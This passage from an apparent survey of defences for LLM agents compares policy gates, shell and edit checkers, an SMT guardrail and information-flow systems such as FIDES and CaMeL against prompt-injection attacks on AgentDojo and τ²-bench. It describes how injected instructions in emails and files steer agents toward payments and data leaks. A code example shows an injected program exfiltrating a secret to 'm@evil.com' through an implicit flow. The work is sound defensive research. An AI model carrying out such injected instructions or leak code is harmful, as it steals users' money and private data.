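After the code merged duplicates and dropped minority drafts, 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules remained. In a separate test with all the checks switched off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not work. A larger commercial model made two of the same kinds of mistake, so the checks would probably still be needed even with a better drafter.

### A rule that blocks forever and a rule that never blocks

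The retail policy requires the agent to authenticate each customer at the start by looking up an email address or a name and postcode. The model turned this clause into a rule that blocked all tools until the customer was authenticated, including the two lookup tools used for authentication. If the gate had enforced this rule, no conversation could have got past authentication. The check found both lookup tools in the table of tools that lift the condition and removed them from the tools the rule blocked.

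This check examines one rule at a time, so it misses pairs of rules in which each rule blocks the tool that would lift the other. Yu and colleagues wrote such a pair, and their gate loaded it without an error.

The policies compiled for AgentDojo had the opposite defect. One condition, `recipient_unknown`, blocks messages and payments to anyone the user has not named by checking the `recipient` argument. The model also attached it to tools without that argument, such as an email tool whose argument is called `recipients`. On those tools the condition is always false, so the prohibition never blocks anything.

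An added check detects this mismatch from the schemas and substitutes a broader condition that examines whichever argument names the target. On the Slack suite, this repair reduced the attacks that took effect from 15 of 105 pairs to none, but it also reduced benign utility from 57.1% to 14.3%. Because a rule that never fires raises no false alarms, some of the original utility depended on the protection not working.

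Schemas can't be used to catch a rule that runs but misstates the policy. For example, a telecom policy tells the agent to check that a bill is overdue before it sends a payment request. The model drafted a rule that forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue, the only time they are appropriate. To catch such mistakes, NOMOS replays its rules over recorded conversations of an agent that ran without a gate. This rule would have refused 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful conversations. NOMOS flags a rule if it refuses at least 90% of the calls to a tool in successful conversations, so a rule that wrongly refused half of them would pass.

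### Task success and violations with the NOMOS gate

The researchers ran τ²-bench with the openly available language model gemma-4-26B as the agent. They counted violations by checking each call that changed data against a separate set of rules they had written by hand.

| | Airline, no gate | Airline, gate | Retail, no gate | Retail, gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Data-changing calls that break a rule | 234 of 353 (66.3%) | 3 of 116 (2.6%) | 188 of 611 (30.8%) | 40 of 582 (6.9%) |
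| Tasks completed | 39.2% | 47.6% | 52.4% | 50.2% |

Neither change in task completion is statistically significant for a single attempt. On the airline tasks, the share that the agent completed in both of two attempts rose from 27.4% to 40.6%, a statistically significant increase.

The benchmark checks the final state of the database, so an agent that cancels a flight against the policy fails the task. A gate can raise task success by blocking that cancellation. But an agent can also pass some tasks easily by changing nothing. With a second model, Llama-3.3-70B, the airline agent completed 46.8% of its 250 runs behind the gate, up from 22.8% without it, and made only 28 data changes. At least 89 of its 117 successful runs therefore changed no data. Because doing nothing is often correct, the benchmark does not penalise needless blocks very much.

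Yu and colleagues also examined 109 calls that the gate would have refused in conversations that the agent had completed successfully without a gate. They had another language model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, judge these calls, and it rated 57 of them permissible. Whether 48 of the 57 were false alarms depends on how one reads the policy, which requires the customer's explicit confirmation before a change. The gate requires a new "yes" for every change, while the judge accepted one "yes" for several changes announced together. The transcripts showed that the judge was wrong about six more. The remaining three were clear false alarms: the policy forbids changes to basic economy flights but permits cabin upgrades, and the gate's rule blocked both. The judge had wrongly accepted a fourth refusal of this kind.

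Under the strict reading of the confirmation clause, 4 of the 109 refusals (about 4%) were false alarms, compared with 52 (about 48%) under the lenient reading. The handwritten rules could not have exposed the basic economy mistake, because they contain it too. They matched all 228 refusals that the compiled airline rules produced in a replay.

### The cost on AgentDojo

AgentDojo has no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote a one-page policy for each suite. Some clauses in the Slack, travel and workspace policies name the attacks' targets, which probably helps the gate.

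| Suite | Attack success, no gate | Attack success, gate | Benign utility, no gate | Benign utility, gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5% | 0.0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Workspace | 7.3% | 0.0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |

The utility losses on banking and travel are within the range of chance, since these suites have only 16 and 20 user tasks, but the losses on workspace and Slack are not. Most of the loss comes from the rule that the agent may act only on targets the user has named. In Slack, users ask for things like a summary of an article a colleague has posted. The link is in the colleague's message, not the user's request, so the gate can't distinguish it from a link planted by an attacker.

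The banking rule is looser, since it also accepts anyone in the account's transaction history. It still blocks the real payment in the bill task, because the correct account number, like the attacker's, appears only in the file. Progent, another system that the researchers ran on the suite, instead let some payments to the attacker through, because it drafts a new policy from each user request and a request to pay a bill does not name an account. Progent let 5.6% of attacks succeed and had a benign utility of 62.5%.

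Among the defences that come with AgentDojo, repeating the user's request to the model kept benign utility at 83.3% on banking but let 31.9% of attacks succeed. A filter that removes tools before each task reduced the attack success rate to 11.8% and benign utility to 58.3%.

Despite the zero for banking, some injected instructions had an effect. In 8 of 288 pairs, the agent behind the gate reacted to an injected instruction by paying someone in the transaction history. The rule allows such payments, and the benchmark does not count them because the attacker did not receive the money. To tell the real bill from the planted instruction, a gate would need more information about where each value came from, which the information-flow defences in the next section record.

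### Shell commands

The conditions in NOMOS depend on how a person or a model interpreted a policy. *Look Before You Leap* (Althoubi, 2026) tests a check with a more objective standard, whether a shell command is valid on the machine where it would run. The experiment uses 1,986 valid commands from a public collection of examples and 7,944 invalid ones made by altering commands. A quarter of the invalid commands name a program that doesn't exist, a quarter have broken syntax, and the rest use a long or short option that the program doesn't accept. The 9,930 commands cover 482 installed programs.

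One shell-command checker applies three tests before a command runs. It uses the shell to parse the command without running it, looks up whether the program exists, and compares each option with a list taken from the program's help text and manual page. The three tests caught 95.8% of the invalid commands and wrongly rejected 198 valid ones, a false-positive rate of 10.0%.

The syntax and program tests produced none of these false alarms. The syntax test uses the same parser that would read the command anyway, so any command it rejects is malformed, and a program that the lookup can't find will not start. The two tests caught every syntax error and missing program, which together make up half of the invalid commands. However, Althoubi points out that in practice the parser rejects incomplete fragments and the lookup misses aliases and functions defined within the shell, so a gate should not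 block in those cases.

All 198 false alarms came from the option test, because help texts are incomplete and the code that extracts options from them sometimes misses some. If a program accepts an option that is missing from the extracted list, the checker rejects a valid command. For about 9% of the programs, the checker finds no options and lets the command through, which avoids more false alarms but misses some errors. The test caught 91.6% of the invalid options.

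### What it costs to be unsure

To reduce false alarms, Althoubi changed the checker to give no verdict on options with one dash and several letters, such as `-la`. These are the most ambiguous cases because they may be a single option or two options written together. The false-positive rate fell from 10.0% to 7.0%, and the checker caught as many invalid commands as before. However, none of the invalid commands in the benchmark has an option of this form, so the change could not have reduced detections on this benchmark. If an agent wrote `find . -nme notes.txt` instead of `-name`, the revised checker would not flag the error. It would also still reject some valid options with two dashes, such as the British spelling `--colour`, if they were missing from its list.

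As with APSIS, precision depends on how common errors are. If 5% of commands were invalid, precision would be only about 42%, even at the lower false-positive rate. In a small test with a Claude model, all 42 commands were valid. Althoubi therefore proposes blocking a command only when it fails the syntax or program test, and attaching a warning when an option looks wrong, so that the agent can ignore a false alarm.

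He made the opposite choice for code edits, so the checker refuses them when it is unsure. A program usually prints an error when given a wrong option, but a misplaced edit can damage a file without any message. To measure this, he prepared 640 edits to 224 Python files and set the correct result of each in advance. He then wrote the edits in different formats and changed the files slightly, as if someone had modified them after the agent read them.

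After a shift of one line, 99.1% of edits that specify line numbers changed the wrong lines without an error. Edits that quote the code to be replaced never silently changed the wrong lines when the match had to be exact, but they often found no match after a change in indentation. With approximate matching, 97.7% of single edits went in the right place and 2.3% in the wrong one. When an edit had several separate parts, 39% of approximate matches were wrong but raised no error.

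Althoubi's stricter method, Robust-Apply, accepts an approximate match only if it is at least 90% similar to the quoted code and clearly better than the next best match. It made one silent mistake in 8,320 trials. But on the altered files it completed only 51% of single edits, compared with 98% for the approximate method. In 1,000 such edits, it would avoid about 23 of the approximate method's silent mistakes but refuse about 470 edits that the approximate method would have made correctly, or roughly 20 for each mistake avoided.

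The harm from refusals depends on how often files change between reading and editing, because Robust-Apply refused no edits that quote the surrounding code when the files were unaltered. A refusal may also do little harm if the agent reads the file again and retries. Althoubi did not run agents through whole tasks with these checks, so it is unknown how much time refusals waste or how often they lead agents to abandon work.

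### A claim of zero false alarms

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, report that their gate let no attack succeed and raised no false alarms. The gate accepts a tool call only as structured data, translates it into a formula, and uses the SMT solver Z3 to test whether the call is consistent with the current state and a fixed set of rules. It runs the solver on every call, which takes 0.44 milliseconds on average, whereas the policies in an earlier section go through a solver before deployment.

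In the first of two scenarios, an agent may pay out at most 500 yuan a day. The state consists of the total paid so far, o, the daily limit, ℓ, and the agent's privilege level, p. It starts at o = 0, ℓ = 500 and p = 1, and two rules must hold after every call:

o ≤ ℓ

(ℓ ≠ 500) → p ≥ 10

If the agent pays 350 yuan and then requests a payment of 300, the gate blocks the second payment because the total of 650 would break the first rule. The second rule prevents the agent from raising its own limit. Because the gate keeps a running total, it stops split payments that a Cedar rule, which keeps no state, would allow.

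The test set has 30 attempts to split a payment, 30 attempts to change the rules or the privilege level, and 30 ordinary payments. Of the six language models tested, Claude Sonnet 4.6 produced no valid runs. With the other five, the gate blocked all the attacks and allowed all the ordinary payments.

The second scenario is a single attempt, over 12 rounds, to send confidential data out of a company network. It includes no harmless tasks, so the claim of zero false alarms is based on the 30 ordinary payments. That claim deserves little weight for several reasons.

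Wu and colleagues define an ordinary payment as one that satisfies the rules, and the gate blocks exactly the calls that don't. If the code is correct, the false-positive rate is therefore zero whatever the rules are. The test can reveal errors in the translation or the running total, but not rules that are too strict. One prompt classed as an attack is a request to pay an instructor's fee of 600 yuan in a single payment. A company might well want to pay that fee after an approval, but the benchmark counts the refusal as a success.

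The test was also easy. A simple gate with no memory of earlier payments raised no false alarms with any of the five models either. A language model used as a judge raised none with four of them, but with GPT-5.4 it wrongly blocked 2 of the 30 payments. In these harmless tests, the agent had only one tool and was told to convert each request into a payment without refusing, so the results are weak evidence about longer tasks.

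Thirty cases are also too few to establish a low rate. If a gate wrongly blocks a share f of harmless requests, the chance that it blocks none of n independent requests is

(1 − f)ⁿ

A gate that wrongly blocks 5% of requests would still have about a 21% chance of producing no false alarms in 30 cases. At the 95% confidence level, zero false alarms in 30 cases rules out only rates above about 9.5%. Ruling out rates above 1% would take 299 cases without a false alarm. The five models received the same 30 payments, so their results do not count as 150 independent cases. The calculation also assumes that the payments are a random sample of what users ask for, but a script generated them.

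The paper's main proof, which concerns missed violations, shows that no sequence of calls can lead to a state that breaks the rules, provided that every action passes through the gate, nobody can change the rules, and each structured call describes everything the tool will do. The version of `write_file` that also contacts a metrics service would violate the last condition. The formula must also contain every relevant fact. The solver allows a call if it can find any consistent set of values, so if the formula didn't specify the total paid so far, the solver could allow a call by using a total that satisfies the rules.

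Wu and colleagues acknowledge that their experiments illustrate the mechanism and do not provide representative statistics, and that an agent can exploit the gap left by any rule the developers forgot to write. They consider the design better suited to a short list of absolute limits than to broad commercial rules.

The rules in the second scenario show how an absolute limit can cause needless blocks. Once the agent has read confidential data, it cannot return to the public internet for the rest of the session. This stopped the attempt to send the data out, but it would also block a user's request to look up a train time after the agent has read a confidential report.

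## Tracking untrusted data through an agent

The gates in the previous section often refused a message or payment because its target did not appear in the user's request. They had no record of what had influenced the model. Information-flow control adds that record. The harness labels all data the agent handles, works out the label of anything made from that data, and checks the labels before a tool runs. This can guarantee that injected instructions never trigger a protected action, but in its simplest form it also blocks much of what users ask for.

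### Labels and how they combine

An integrity label is either T, for trusted, or U, for untrusted, which means that an outsider could have written the data. A confidentiality label lists the people who may read the data. When the harness combines two pieces of data, the result takes the stricter label of each kind. This operation is called a join and written ⊔:

T ⊔ T = T

T ⊔ U = U

{Ana, Bob, Carol} ⊔ {Bob, Carol, Dan} = {Bob, Carol}

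Text made from two documents is untrusted if either document is, and only people allowed to read both may read it. Dorothy Denning described this scheme for ordinary computer systems in 1976.

The user's request usually starts out trusted and readable by everyone. An email from outside is untrusted and readable only by its sender and recipients. The model's reply is harder to label, because the harness can't determine which parts of the prompt influenced it. The usual solution is to over-approximate by giving the reply the join of the labels of everything in the prompt.

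According to Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, two rules for tool calls cover most practical cases:

- Trusted action: the gate permits a call only if the model chose it in a trusted context. Arguments that matter for safety, such as the recipient of a payment, must also be trusted.
- Permitted flow: the gate permits a call that sends data only if every recipient is among the data's readers.

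Calls that only read data don't have to meet either rule, and calls that send data have to meet only one. A user who asks in their own words to send a private file presumably means it, and an injected instruction that meets only the second rule can't reveal data to anyone who wasn't already allowed to read it.

The property behind such rules is non-interference, which Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined in 1982. Write x ~ y if two inputs agree on everything labelled T and may differ in everything labelled U. A program P satisfies non-interference if

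x ~ y → P(x) ~ P(y)

If an attacker rewrites an email, the trusted part of the outcome, including every protected action, stays the same, but the untrusted part, such as a summary of the email, may change. The same definition applies to secrets, where changing a secret input must not change anything public.

### How one email blocks a harmless message

Suppose a user writes, "Show me Carol's latest email, then tell Bob I'll be ten minutes late." The agent keeps one label for its whole context, which is everything the model has seen so far.

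| Step | Label of the new item | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request arrives | T, everyone | T, everyone |
| The model requests `read_email`, and the gate allows it because it only reads | T, everyone | T, everyone |
| The harness adds Carol's email | U, {user, Carol} | U, {user, Carol} |
| The model requests `send_message` to Bob | U, {user, Carol} | the gate blocks the call |

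The call fails both rules. The model chose it in an untrusted context, and Bob is not among the readers. The text "I'll be ten minutes late" contains nothing from the email, but the harness can't establish that, since an instruction hidden in the email could have produced an identical call. If the agent had messaged Bob before opening the email, the gate would have allowed both calls. It would also have allowed the message if Carol had addressed her email to Bob too.

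Joins never make a label less strict, so the context stays untrusted for the rest of the session and the same restriction applies to every later message. Researchers call this label spread, or label creep. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) measured its effect on task completion in AgentDojo runs without attacks, using an agent based on GPT-4o. Without a defence, the agent completed 98.8% of the banking tasks and 93.3% of the Slack tasks. With one label for the whole context and the rules switched on, it completed 37.5% and 20.0%.

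Dividing the work differently among tools and agents helps only partly. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) varied the size and layout of simulated agent systems and found that layout strongly affects how far labels spread, but that no layout fully prevents the loss.

### Keeping untrusted text out of the context

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, gives each value its own label. When a tool returns data with a stricter label than the context has, the harness stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. In the example, the model sees something like `#read_email_0.body#` in place of the text of Carol's email. The context stays trusted, so the gate allows the message to Bob. The model can still put the variable's name in its final answer, and the harness can show the user the email's text.

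The model can also pass a variable to a tool without reading it. If the user asks the agent to forward Carol's email to Bob, the call and the recipient are trusted and only the message body is untrusted, so the call meets the rule FIDES uses for messages. However, the model can't summarise text it can't see or use that text to choose its next step. If the model opens the variable, the whole context becomes untrusted again.

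To let an agent process hidden text, FIDES uses a second, quarantined model that has no tools, a division Simon Willison proposed in 2023 as the dual-LLM pattern. The main model asks for a summary of the variable that holds the text, the quarantined model writes one, and the harness stores it in a new untrusted variable. An injected instruction can still spoil the summary, such as by making it empty, but it can't trigger a tool call. The extra steps add to the cost. Kolluri and colleagues estimated that the average Slack task with GPT-4o cost 0.5 cents with one label for the whole context and 2.2 cents with FIDES.

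Some tasks need a decision based on untrusted text, such as "if one of my emails asks for a meeting, create the event". FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's answer to yes or no and let the main model read only that answer. An answer with n possible values carries at most log₂ n bits, so a yes or no carries at most one. The rule can allow this because one bit is too little to carry an instruction. This gives up strict non-interference because whoever writes the email decides whether the agent creates an event. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of their AgentDojo tests because few tasks there needed it.

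For secrets, FIDES guarantees a weaker property called explicit secrecy, which covers data that the agent copies but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choices. If the agent emails a supplier only when a confidential report mentions a merger, the email reveals the merger even if its text is harmless. Costa and colleagues considered full non-interference too restrictive because it would essentially forbid any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret.

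With its rules on, FIDES let no attack in the AgentDojo benchmark succeed by the researchers' count, while 152 succeeded against the undefended GPT-4o agent. Under AgentDojo's own scoring, which can count blocked calls as successes, three attacks succeeded against FIDES. With the rules off, 21 succeeded, because the main model could open variables and then act on what it read.

### Which tasks are lost, and why

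Costa and colleagues also tested o1, a reasoning model from OpenAI. They sorted the AgentDojo tasks by whether the right sequence of actions depends on untrusted text. If it does, the trusted-action rule forbids the task however precise the labels are. The table gives the shares of tasks completed with o1, in the version of the paper from May 2025:

| Suite | No defence | Rules on, one label for the context | Rules on, FIDES | Tasks that depend on untrusted text |
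|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 70.0% | 48.0% | 64.5% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 37.5% | 56.2% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 87.6% | 17.1% | 54.3% | 42.9% |

The average over the four suites is 84% without a defence and 61% with FIDES. With GPT-4o the corresponding averages are 84% and 50%.

The rule causes most of FIDES's losses on banking and Slack. Seven of the 16 banking tasks depend on untrusted text, typically because the user asks the agent to read a file and do what it says. Reading the file makes the context untrusted, and the gate then refuses the payment. The other nine tasks are about 56% of the total, which is also the share FIDES completed. The match is partly luck, because the agent also completed some tasks that should have been out of reach. In one, with GPT-4o, the user asked for a new password if any transaction looked suspicious.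 The agent saw a large amount, which is a trusted field, and changed the password without reading the untrusted description.

Using one coarse label for the whole context instead of FIDES lowers task completion by 37 percentage points on Slack and about 19 on banking. In these lost tasks, as in the message to Bob, the untrusted text had no bearing on the action.

Workspace losses have another cause: in most of the lost tasks, the model did not take a route that the rules permitted. Only 5% of Workspace tasks depend on untrusted text, yet switching on the rules lowered FIDES's score from 77.5% to 64.5%. Costa and colleagues describe similar errors with GPT-4o, which mixed up variable names and called tools it didn't need, including one that made the context untrusted. On travel tasks, FIDES did worse than the single label. Many travel tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context as long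 as no private data leaks, so hiding text helped little and made the work harder for the model.

Labels can also be too coarse when data first enters the system. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted everywhere if any attack in the benchmark used it. In one workspace task, the user wants a password reset link from a recent email, and the agent fails because it can't tell trusted senders from untrusted ones. Mail servers can authenticate sender addresses, so a label based on the verified sender could let the agent complete this task without weakening the rule.

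### Newer models and endorsement by a person

Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also worked on FIDES, ran it again with other models in February 2026. They added their own agent, Prudentia, which uses FIDES's labels and tells the model which rules apply to each tool. Before Prudentia opens a variable, it has to write down why it needs to and what it will do next. The table shows the share of all AgentDojo tasks that each agent completed without asking a person for anything, next to an undefended agent:

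| Model | No defence | One label for the context | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 72.2% | 38.4% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 62.5% | 35.5% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 70.1% | 42.5% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 72.3% | 43.4% | 57.1% | 72.7% |

With GPT-5, Prudentia did as well as the undefended agent, which supports the idea that many of the earlier losses came from poor planning. But it completed 80.0% of tasks when a person could approve calls that broke a rule, so the rules still lowered its completion rate by about seven points. Costa and colleagues classify about 20 of the 97 tasks as dependent on untrusted text, so an agent that never asks for approval could complete at most about 79%.

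Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of text, which relabels it from U to T. Suppose an outside email lists ten tasks that each need a protected call. If the agent opens the email without endorsement, the context becomes untrusted and the user must approve all ten calls. If the user endorses the email, that one approval covers all ten calls, but it would also cover any task that an attacker had added and the user had overlooked.

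In Prudentia, the agent decides whether to ask the user to endorse untrusted text. When a user wanted only summaries of calendar entries and a link, the agent opened the text without endorsement because no protected call would follow. Over its completed tasks with GPT-5, Prudentia needed about 7 human answers in total, compared with 41 for FIDES.

A person is not needed if the harness can estimate which inputs influenced a call. *Sightline* (2026) tests this on AgentDojo with an agent based on the small model Qwen3-8B. It removed 50.0% of the labels that came from irrelevant inputs and missed a real influence in 3.9% of episodes. No attack in the test got past the integrity rule. But the guarantee is then only statistical, and an attacker could look for text whose influence the method misses. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists such graded labels as an open problem, along with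 deciding which pieces of the context should have their own label. For example, a web agent could label text by the site it came from.

### CaMeL

In CaMeL (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025), a privileged model writes its whole plan as a Python program, based on the user's request, before it sees any untrusted data. A quarantined model extracts values from untrusted text while the program runs. An interpreter executes the program, tracks where each value came from, and checks the rules before each tool call (*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security*, 2025). For the request about Carol and Bob, the program would read the email, show it, and call `send_message` with a recipient and text copied from the user's request. Both arguments are trusted, so the gate allows the call.

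The program can branch on untrusted values, but untrusted text can't add steps to it. In FIDES, by contrast, the main model can read a variable's contents and plan again, but its context then becomes untrusted.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls the drop in completed tasks with CaMeL on AgentDojo comparatively modest, and *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* describes CaMeL's performance as comparable to an unprotected agent's. A rerun by Garby, Gordon and Sands in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (2026) got less favourable results. On the banking suite with GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 66.7% of runs with its rule checks off and 37.5% with them on. With MiMo-v2.5, the figures were 70.8% and 37.5%. The rerun did not include an undefended agent, and even with the checks off, CaMeL still plans in advance and uses a quarantined model.

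Task completion is also low on the Slack suite. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes an agent that lets a helper model keep using tools after reading untrusted text, within the limits its labels set. With rules on, this agent completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL. Garby and colleagues quote a much smaller gap from the same project, 8 of 21 tasks against CaMeL's 7, perhaps from a different version or model. Without rules, the project's agent completed 15 of the 21.

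CaMeL has no proof of non-interference, and Garby and colleagues found two ways for secrets to leak through its tracking. In the first, an injected instruction leads to a program like this one:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` keeps its public label and the gate allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is high, although no secret value was copied into the email.

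The second leak is in the ordinary Python loop that restarts CaMeL after an error. Whether the rules blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, and the loop doesn't track that dependence. An attacker who gets the agent to retry many times could learn the secret one bit at a time.

### The LLMbda calculus

Closing the first leak makes a system stricter. Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, the LLMbda calculus, in which a program stops if it tries to write to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret. This rule also stops programs whose author meant no harm.

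The calculus extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which everything is a function. Every value and the conversation with the model have labels. A program can send the model a prompt, run code that the model writes, and test or demand a particular label. It can also `fork` a conversation to make a temporary copy and `clear` a conversation to empty it. With these two commands, the program can build its own quarantined model. It forks the conversation, clears the copy, has the model read the email there, and keeps only the answer. The email never enters the main conversation, so that conversation's label stays trusted. Programs can express this isolation themselves, so the language does not prescribe the architecture of CaMeL or FIDES.

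The main theorem is a form of non-interference for programs whose results are partly random, as a language model's are. Take two starting states that look the same to an observer who sees only data up to a certain label. Let μ₀ and μ₁ give the probabilities of each final result that this observer can distinguish. They may sum to less than 1, because some runs never finish or stop at a broken rule. The theorem guarantees that some distribution ω, with a total of at most 1, satisfies

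μ₀ ≤ ω and μ₁ ≤ ω

for every result. If all runs finish, μ₀ and μ₁ must be equal, so hidden data has no effect on what the observer sees. Otherwise the distance between them, measured as half the sum of the absolute differences, is at most the average probability of not finishing. If 10% of runs fail to finish with one email and 20% with another, the distance can be at most 0.15. The theorem therefore still lets a program leak a little through whether it stops.

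The theorem, which Lean has checked, covers every program in the language, including code that the model writes while the agent runs. The Lean interpreter is also the harness that calls the model, so the proof applies to the program that runs rather than to a separate description of it. The proof assumes that tool developers label their data sources correctly and put checks on every sensitive tool.

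### The banking case study

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in the calculus and tested it on AgentDojo's banking suite. An agent that writes code often needs several attempts, and under strict tracking, untrusted data from one failed attempt would make all later ones untrusted. Randori therefore first tries out code on invented data, where reading a file returns a fixed placeholder. It then writes its final program, which may contain endorsements, before it reads any real data.

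Each figure below comes from 16 tasks with three runs each and no attacks:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| Randori without endorsement | not run | 62.5% | 54.2% |
| CaMeL, rules off | 66.7% | not run | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, rules on | 37.5% | not run | 37.5% |

The loss from removing endorsement is uncertain because the 95% confidence intervals extend about 20 points or more on either side. The explanation is still plausible, because three of the tasks require the agent to read a file and act on it, which the rules forbid without endorsement.

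Randori completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL with its rules on, but endorsement explains only part of the difference. Without endorsement, Randori still completed 54.2% of tasks with MiMo-v2.5, nearly 17 points more than CaMeL. Garby and colleagues implemented only some of CaMeL's rules and made them somewhat less strict, which probably contributed to the difference.

Two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. Both used the same task, in which the user asks the agent to pay a bill by following the instructions in a text file, and the attacker has replaced the file's contents. Labels can't distinguish the real bill from the false one because both would come from the same untrusted file. Without endorsement, the gate blocks the false payment, but also the real one. In about two-thirds of the task-attack pairs, the attack needed a tool call that would never appear in the plan for the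 user's task, so planning in advance stopped it without labels.

### When endorsement is safe

Endorsement deliberately breaks non-interference for trust, but a second theorem, also checked in Lean, shows that it can't break non-interference for secrets. Secrets do not reach public results, apart from the small leak through stopping, no matter how much untrusted data a program endorses or what the attacker writes.

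Whether an endorsement can let an attacker trigger a protected action depends on who decided to make it. In the calculus, an endorsement has no effect if untrusted data determined whether the line making it would run, so code that an attacker inserts through an email can't endorse itself. Randori's endorsements take effect because the model writes them before reading any untrusted data.

This protection fails if an earlier endorsement made the attacker's text trusted before it reached the code-writing model. The resulting code would run as trusted, and its endorsements would take effect. Garby and colleagues propose marking every endorsed value and refusing to endorse it again. This restriction would not affect Randori's tasks, because none of them endorses a value twice.

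Another proposal is to endorse only values from a short fixed list of length n, which limits the attacker to log₂ n bits, as with FIDES's restricted answers. If an agent sorts emails into "general", "billing" and "complaint" and uses the category as the subject of its reply, an attacker can choose only among those three subjects. The program has to endorse a copy of the category, then check the copy against the list, and use it only if it is there. If the program checks the untrusted category first, the check itself depends on untrusted data, and endorsing the category afterwards does nothing. Garby and colleagues have no formal proof of the limits that either proposal places on an attacker.

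Neither proposal covers the account number on a bill. It can't come from a short list, and the ban on repeated endorsement does not show that the number is right. Garby and colleagues argue that endorsing the number is justified because the user chose to trust the file's contents by asking the agent to pay the bill in it. Endorsement records that choice in the program, where a reviewer can find it, but the agent will still pay a false bill if someone has tampered with the file.

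## How developers respond to analyser warnings

Developers can ignore a static analyser's warnings, and those who see too many false alarms start to ignore correct warnings too. Several software companies documented this in ordinary software between 2010 and 2019, before LLM agents were in common use.

### How many wrong reports developers tolerate

In these accounts, unlike in the earlier sections, the "false-positive rate" is the share of an analyser's reports that are wrong, so a rate of 20% means a precision of 80%.

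Coverity, a company that began selling a bug finder in 2002, had about 700 customers by the end of 2009. *A Few Billion Lines of Code Later* (Bessey, Block and colleagues, 2010) reports that when more than about 30% of the tool's reports were false, customers ignored the tool and true bugs got lost among the false ones. Customers who had lost trust also dismissed complex but correct reports as false, which lowered their trust further. Coverity therefore aimed for less than 20% false reports. The order of the reports mattered too, because people tended to dismiss the tool if roughly the first three were wrong. If the reports come in random order, the first three are all wrong less than 1% of the time when 20% of reports are wrong, and about 12% of the time when half are.

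Developers at Microsoft wanted fewer false alarms than Coverity's target allowed. Christakis and Bird (2016), in *What Developers Want and Need from Program Analysis*, sent a survey to 2,000 randomly chosen developers at the company, and 375 answered. Of these, 90% would tolerate a false-alarm rate of 5%, 47% would tolerate 15% and 24% would tolerate 20%. Google set a limit of 10% for warnings that developers see during code review, when a second engineer reads a change before it joins the shared code. According to Sadowski, Aftandilian and colleagues (2018), in *Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google*, this limit was somewhat arbitrary at first but turned out to suit developers.

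These figures roughly agree, but none comes from an experiment that varied the share of wrong reports and recorded when people stopped reading them. Coverity's figure comes from a vendor's experience, and Microsoft's from what developers said they would do. Christakis and Bird conclude that high false-positive rates lead developers to abandon analysers, but only 9% of their respondents had ever stopped using one. The main reasons they gave were a change in team policy, a move to another team or company, and the lack of a suitable tool. False positives ranked third among complaints about analysers, behind unwanted checks that are on by default and badly written messages. When the survey made developers choose, 49.3% preferred fewer false positives even if the tool missed some real bugs, and 50.7% preferred to catch more real bugs even with more false positives.

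### Correct reports that nobody acts on

Google measures something different from technical correctness. Sadowski and colleagues call a report an "effective false positive" if developers take no positive action after seeing it, whether or not the report is right:

| | Developer improves the code | Developer does nothing |
|---|---|---|
| Report is technically right | success | effective false positive |
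| Report is technically wrong | success | effective false positive |

A wrong report can still be useful because it may point to unclear code. In an example from Google, an analyser flags calls to `contains` on a hash table, on the assumption that the developer meant to look up a key. Even when the developer meant to look for a value, replacing `contains` with the equivalent `containsValue` makes the code clearer.

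Developers sometimes reject a correct report because they misunderstand it. One Google check reported calls that passed too many arguments to a text-formatting function. The function accepts only the placeholder `%s`, but developers used other placeholders and counted those too. About once a week, a developer complained that a report was wrong, but the reports were always correct. The complaints stopped when the team explained in the message that only `%s` works.

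Coverity's engineers also met developers who rejected correct warnings. One programmer insisted that the C standard allows a program to write one position past the end of an array, which it does not. Customers tended to call any report they didn't understand a false alarm, so the company dropped some analyses that worked but were hard to explain. For many years, these included its checks for errors between parallel threads.

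Interviews suggest that confusing reports are at least as common a complaint as wrong ones. In *Why Don't Software Developers Use Static Analysis Tools to Find Bugs?*, Johnson, Song and colleagues (2013) interviewed 20 developers for 40 to 60 minutes each. Nineteen said the tools' results did not explain well enough what the problem was or what to do about it. Fourteen complained about the output, including its volume and its false positives, and some said the false positives would bother them less if the tool presented its results better. Sixteen of the 20 worked at one large company, and the study did not include anyone who had never used such tools.

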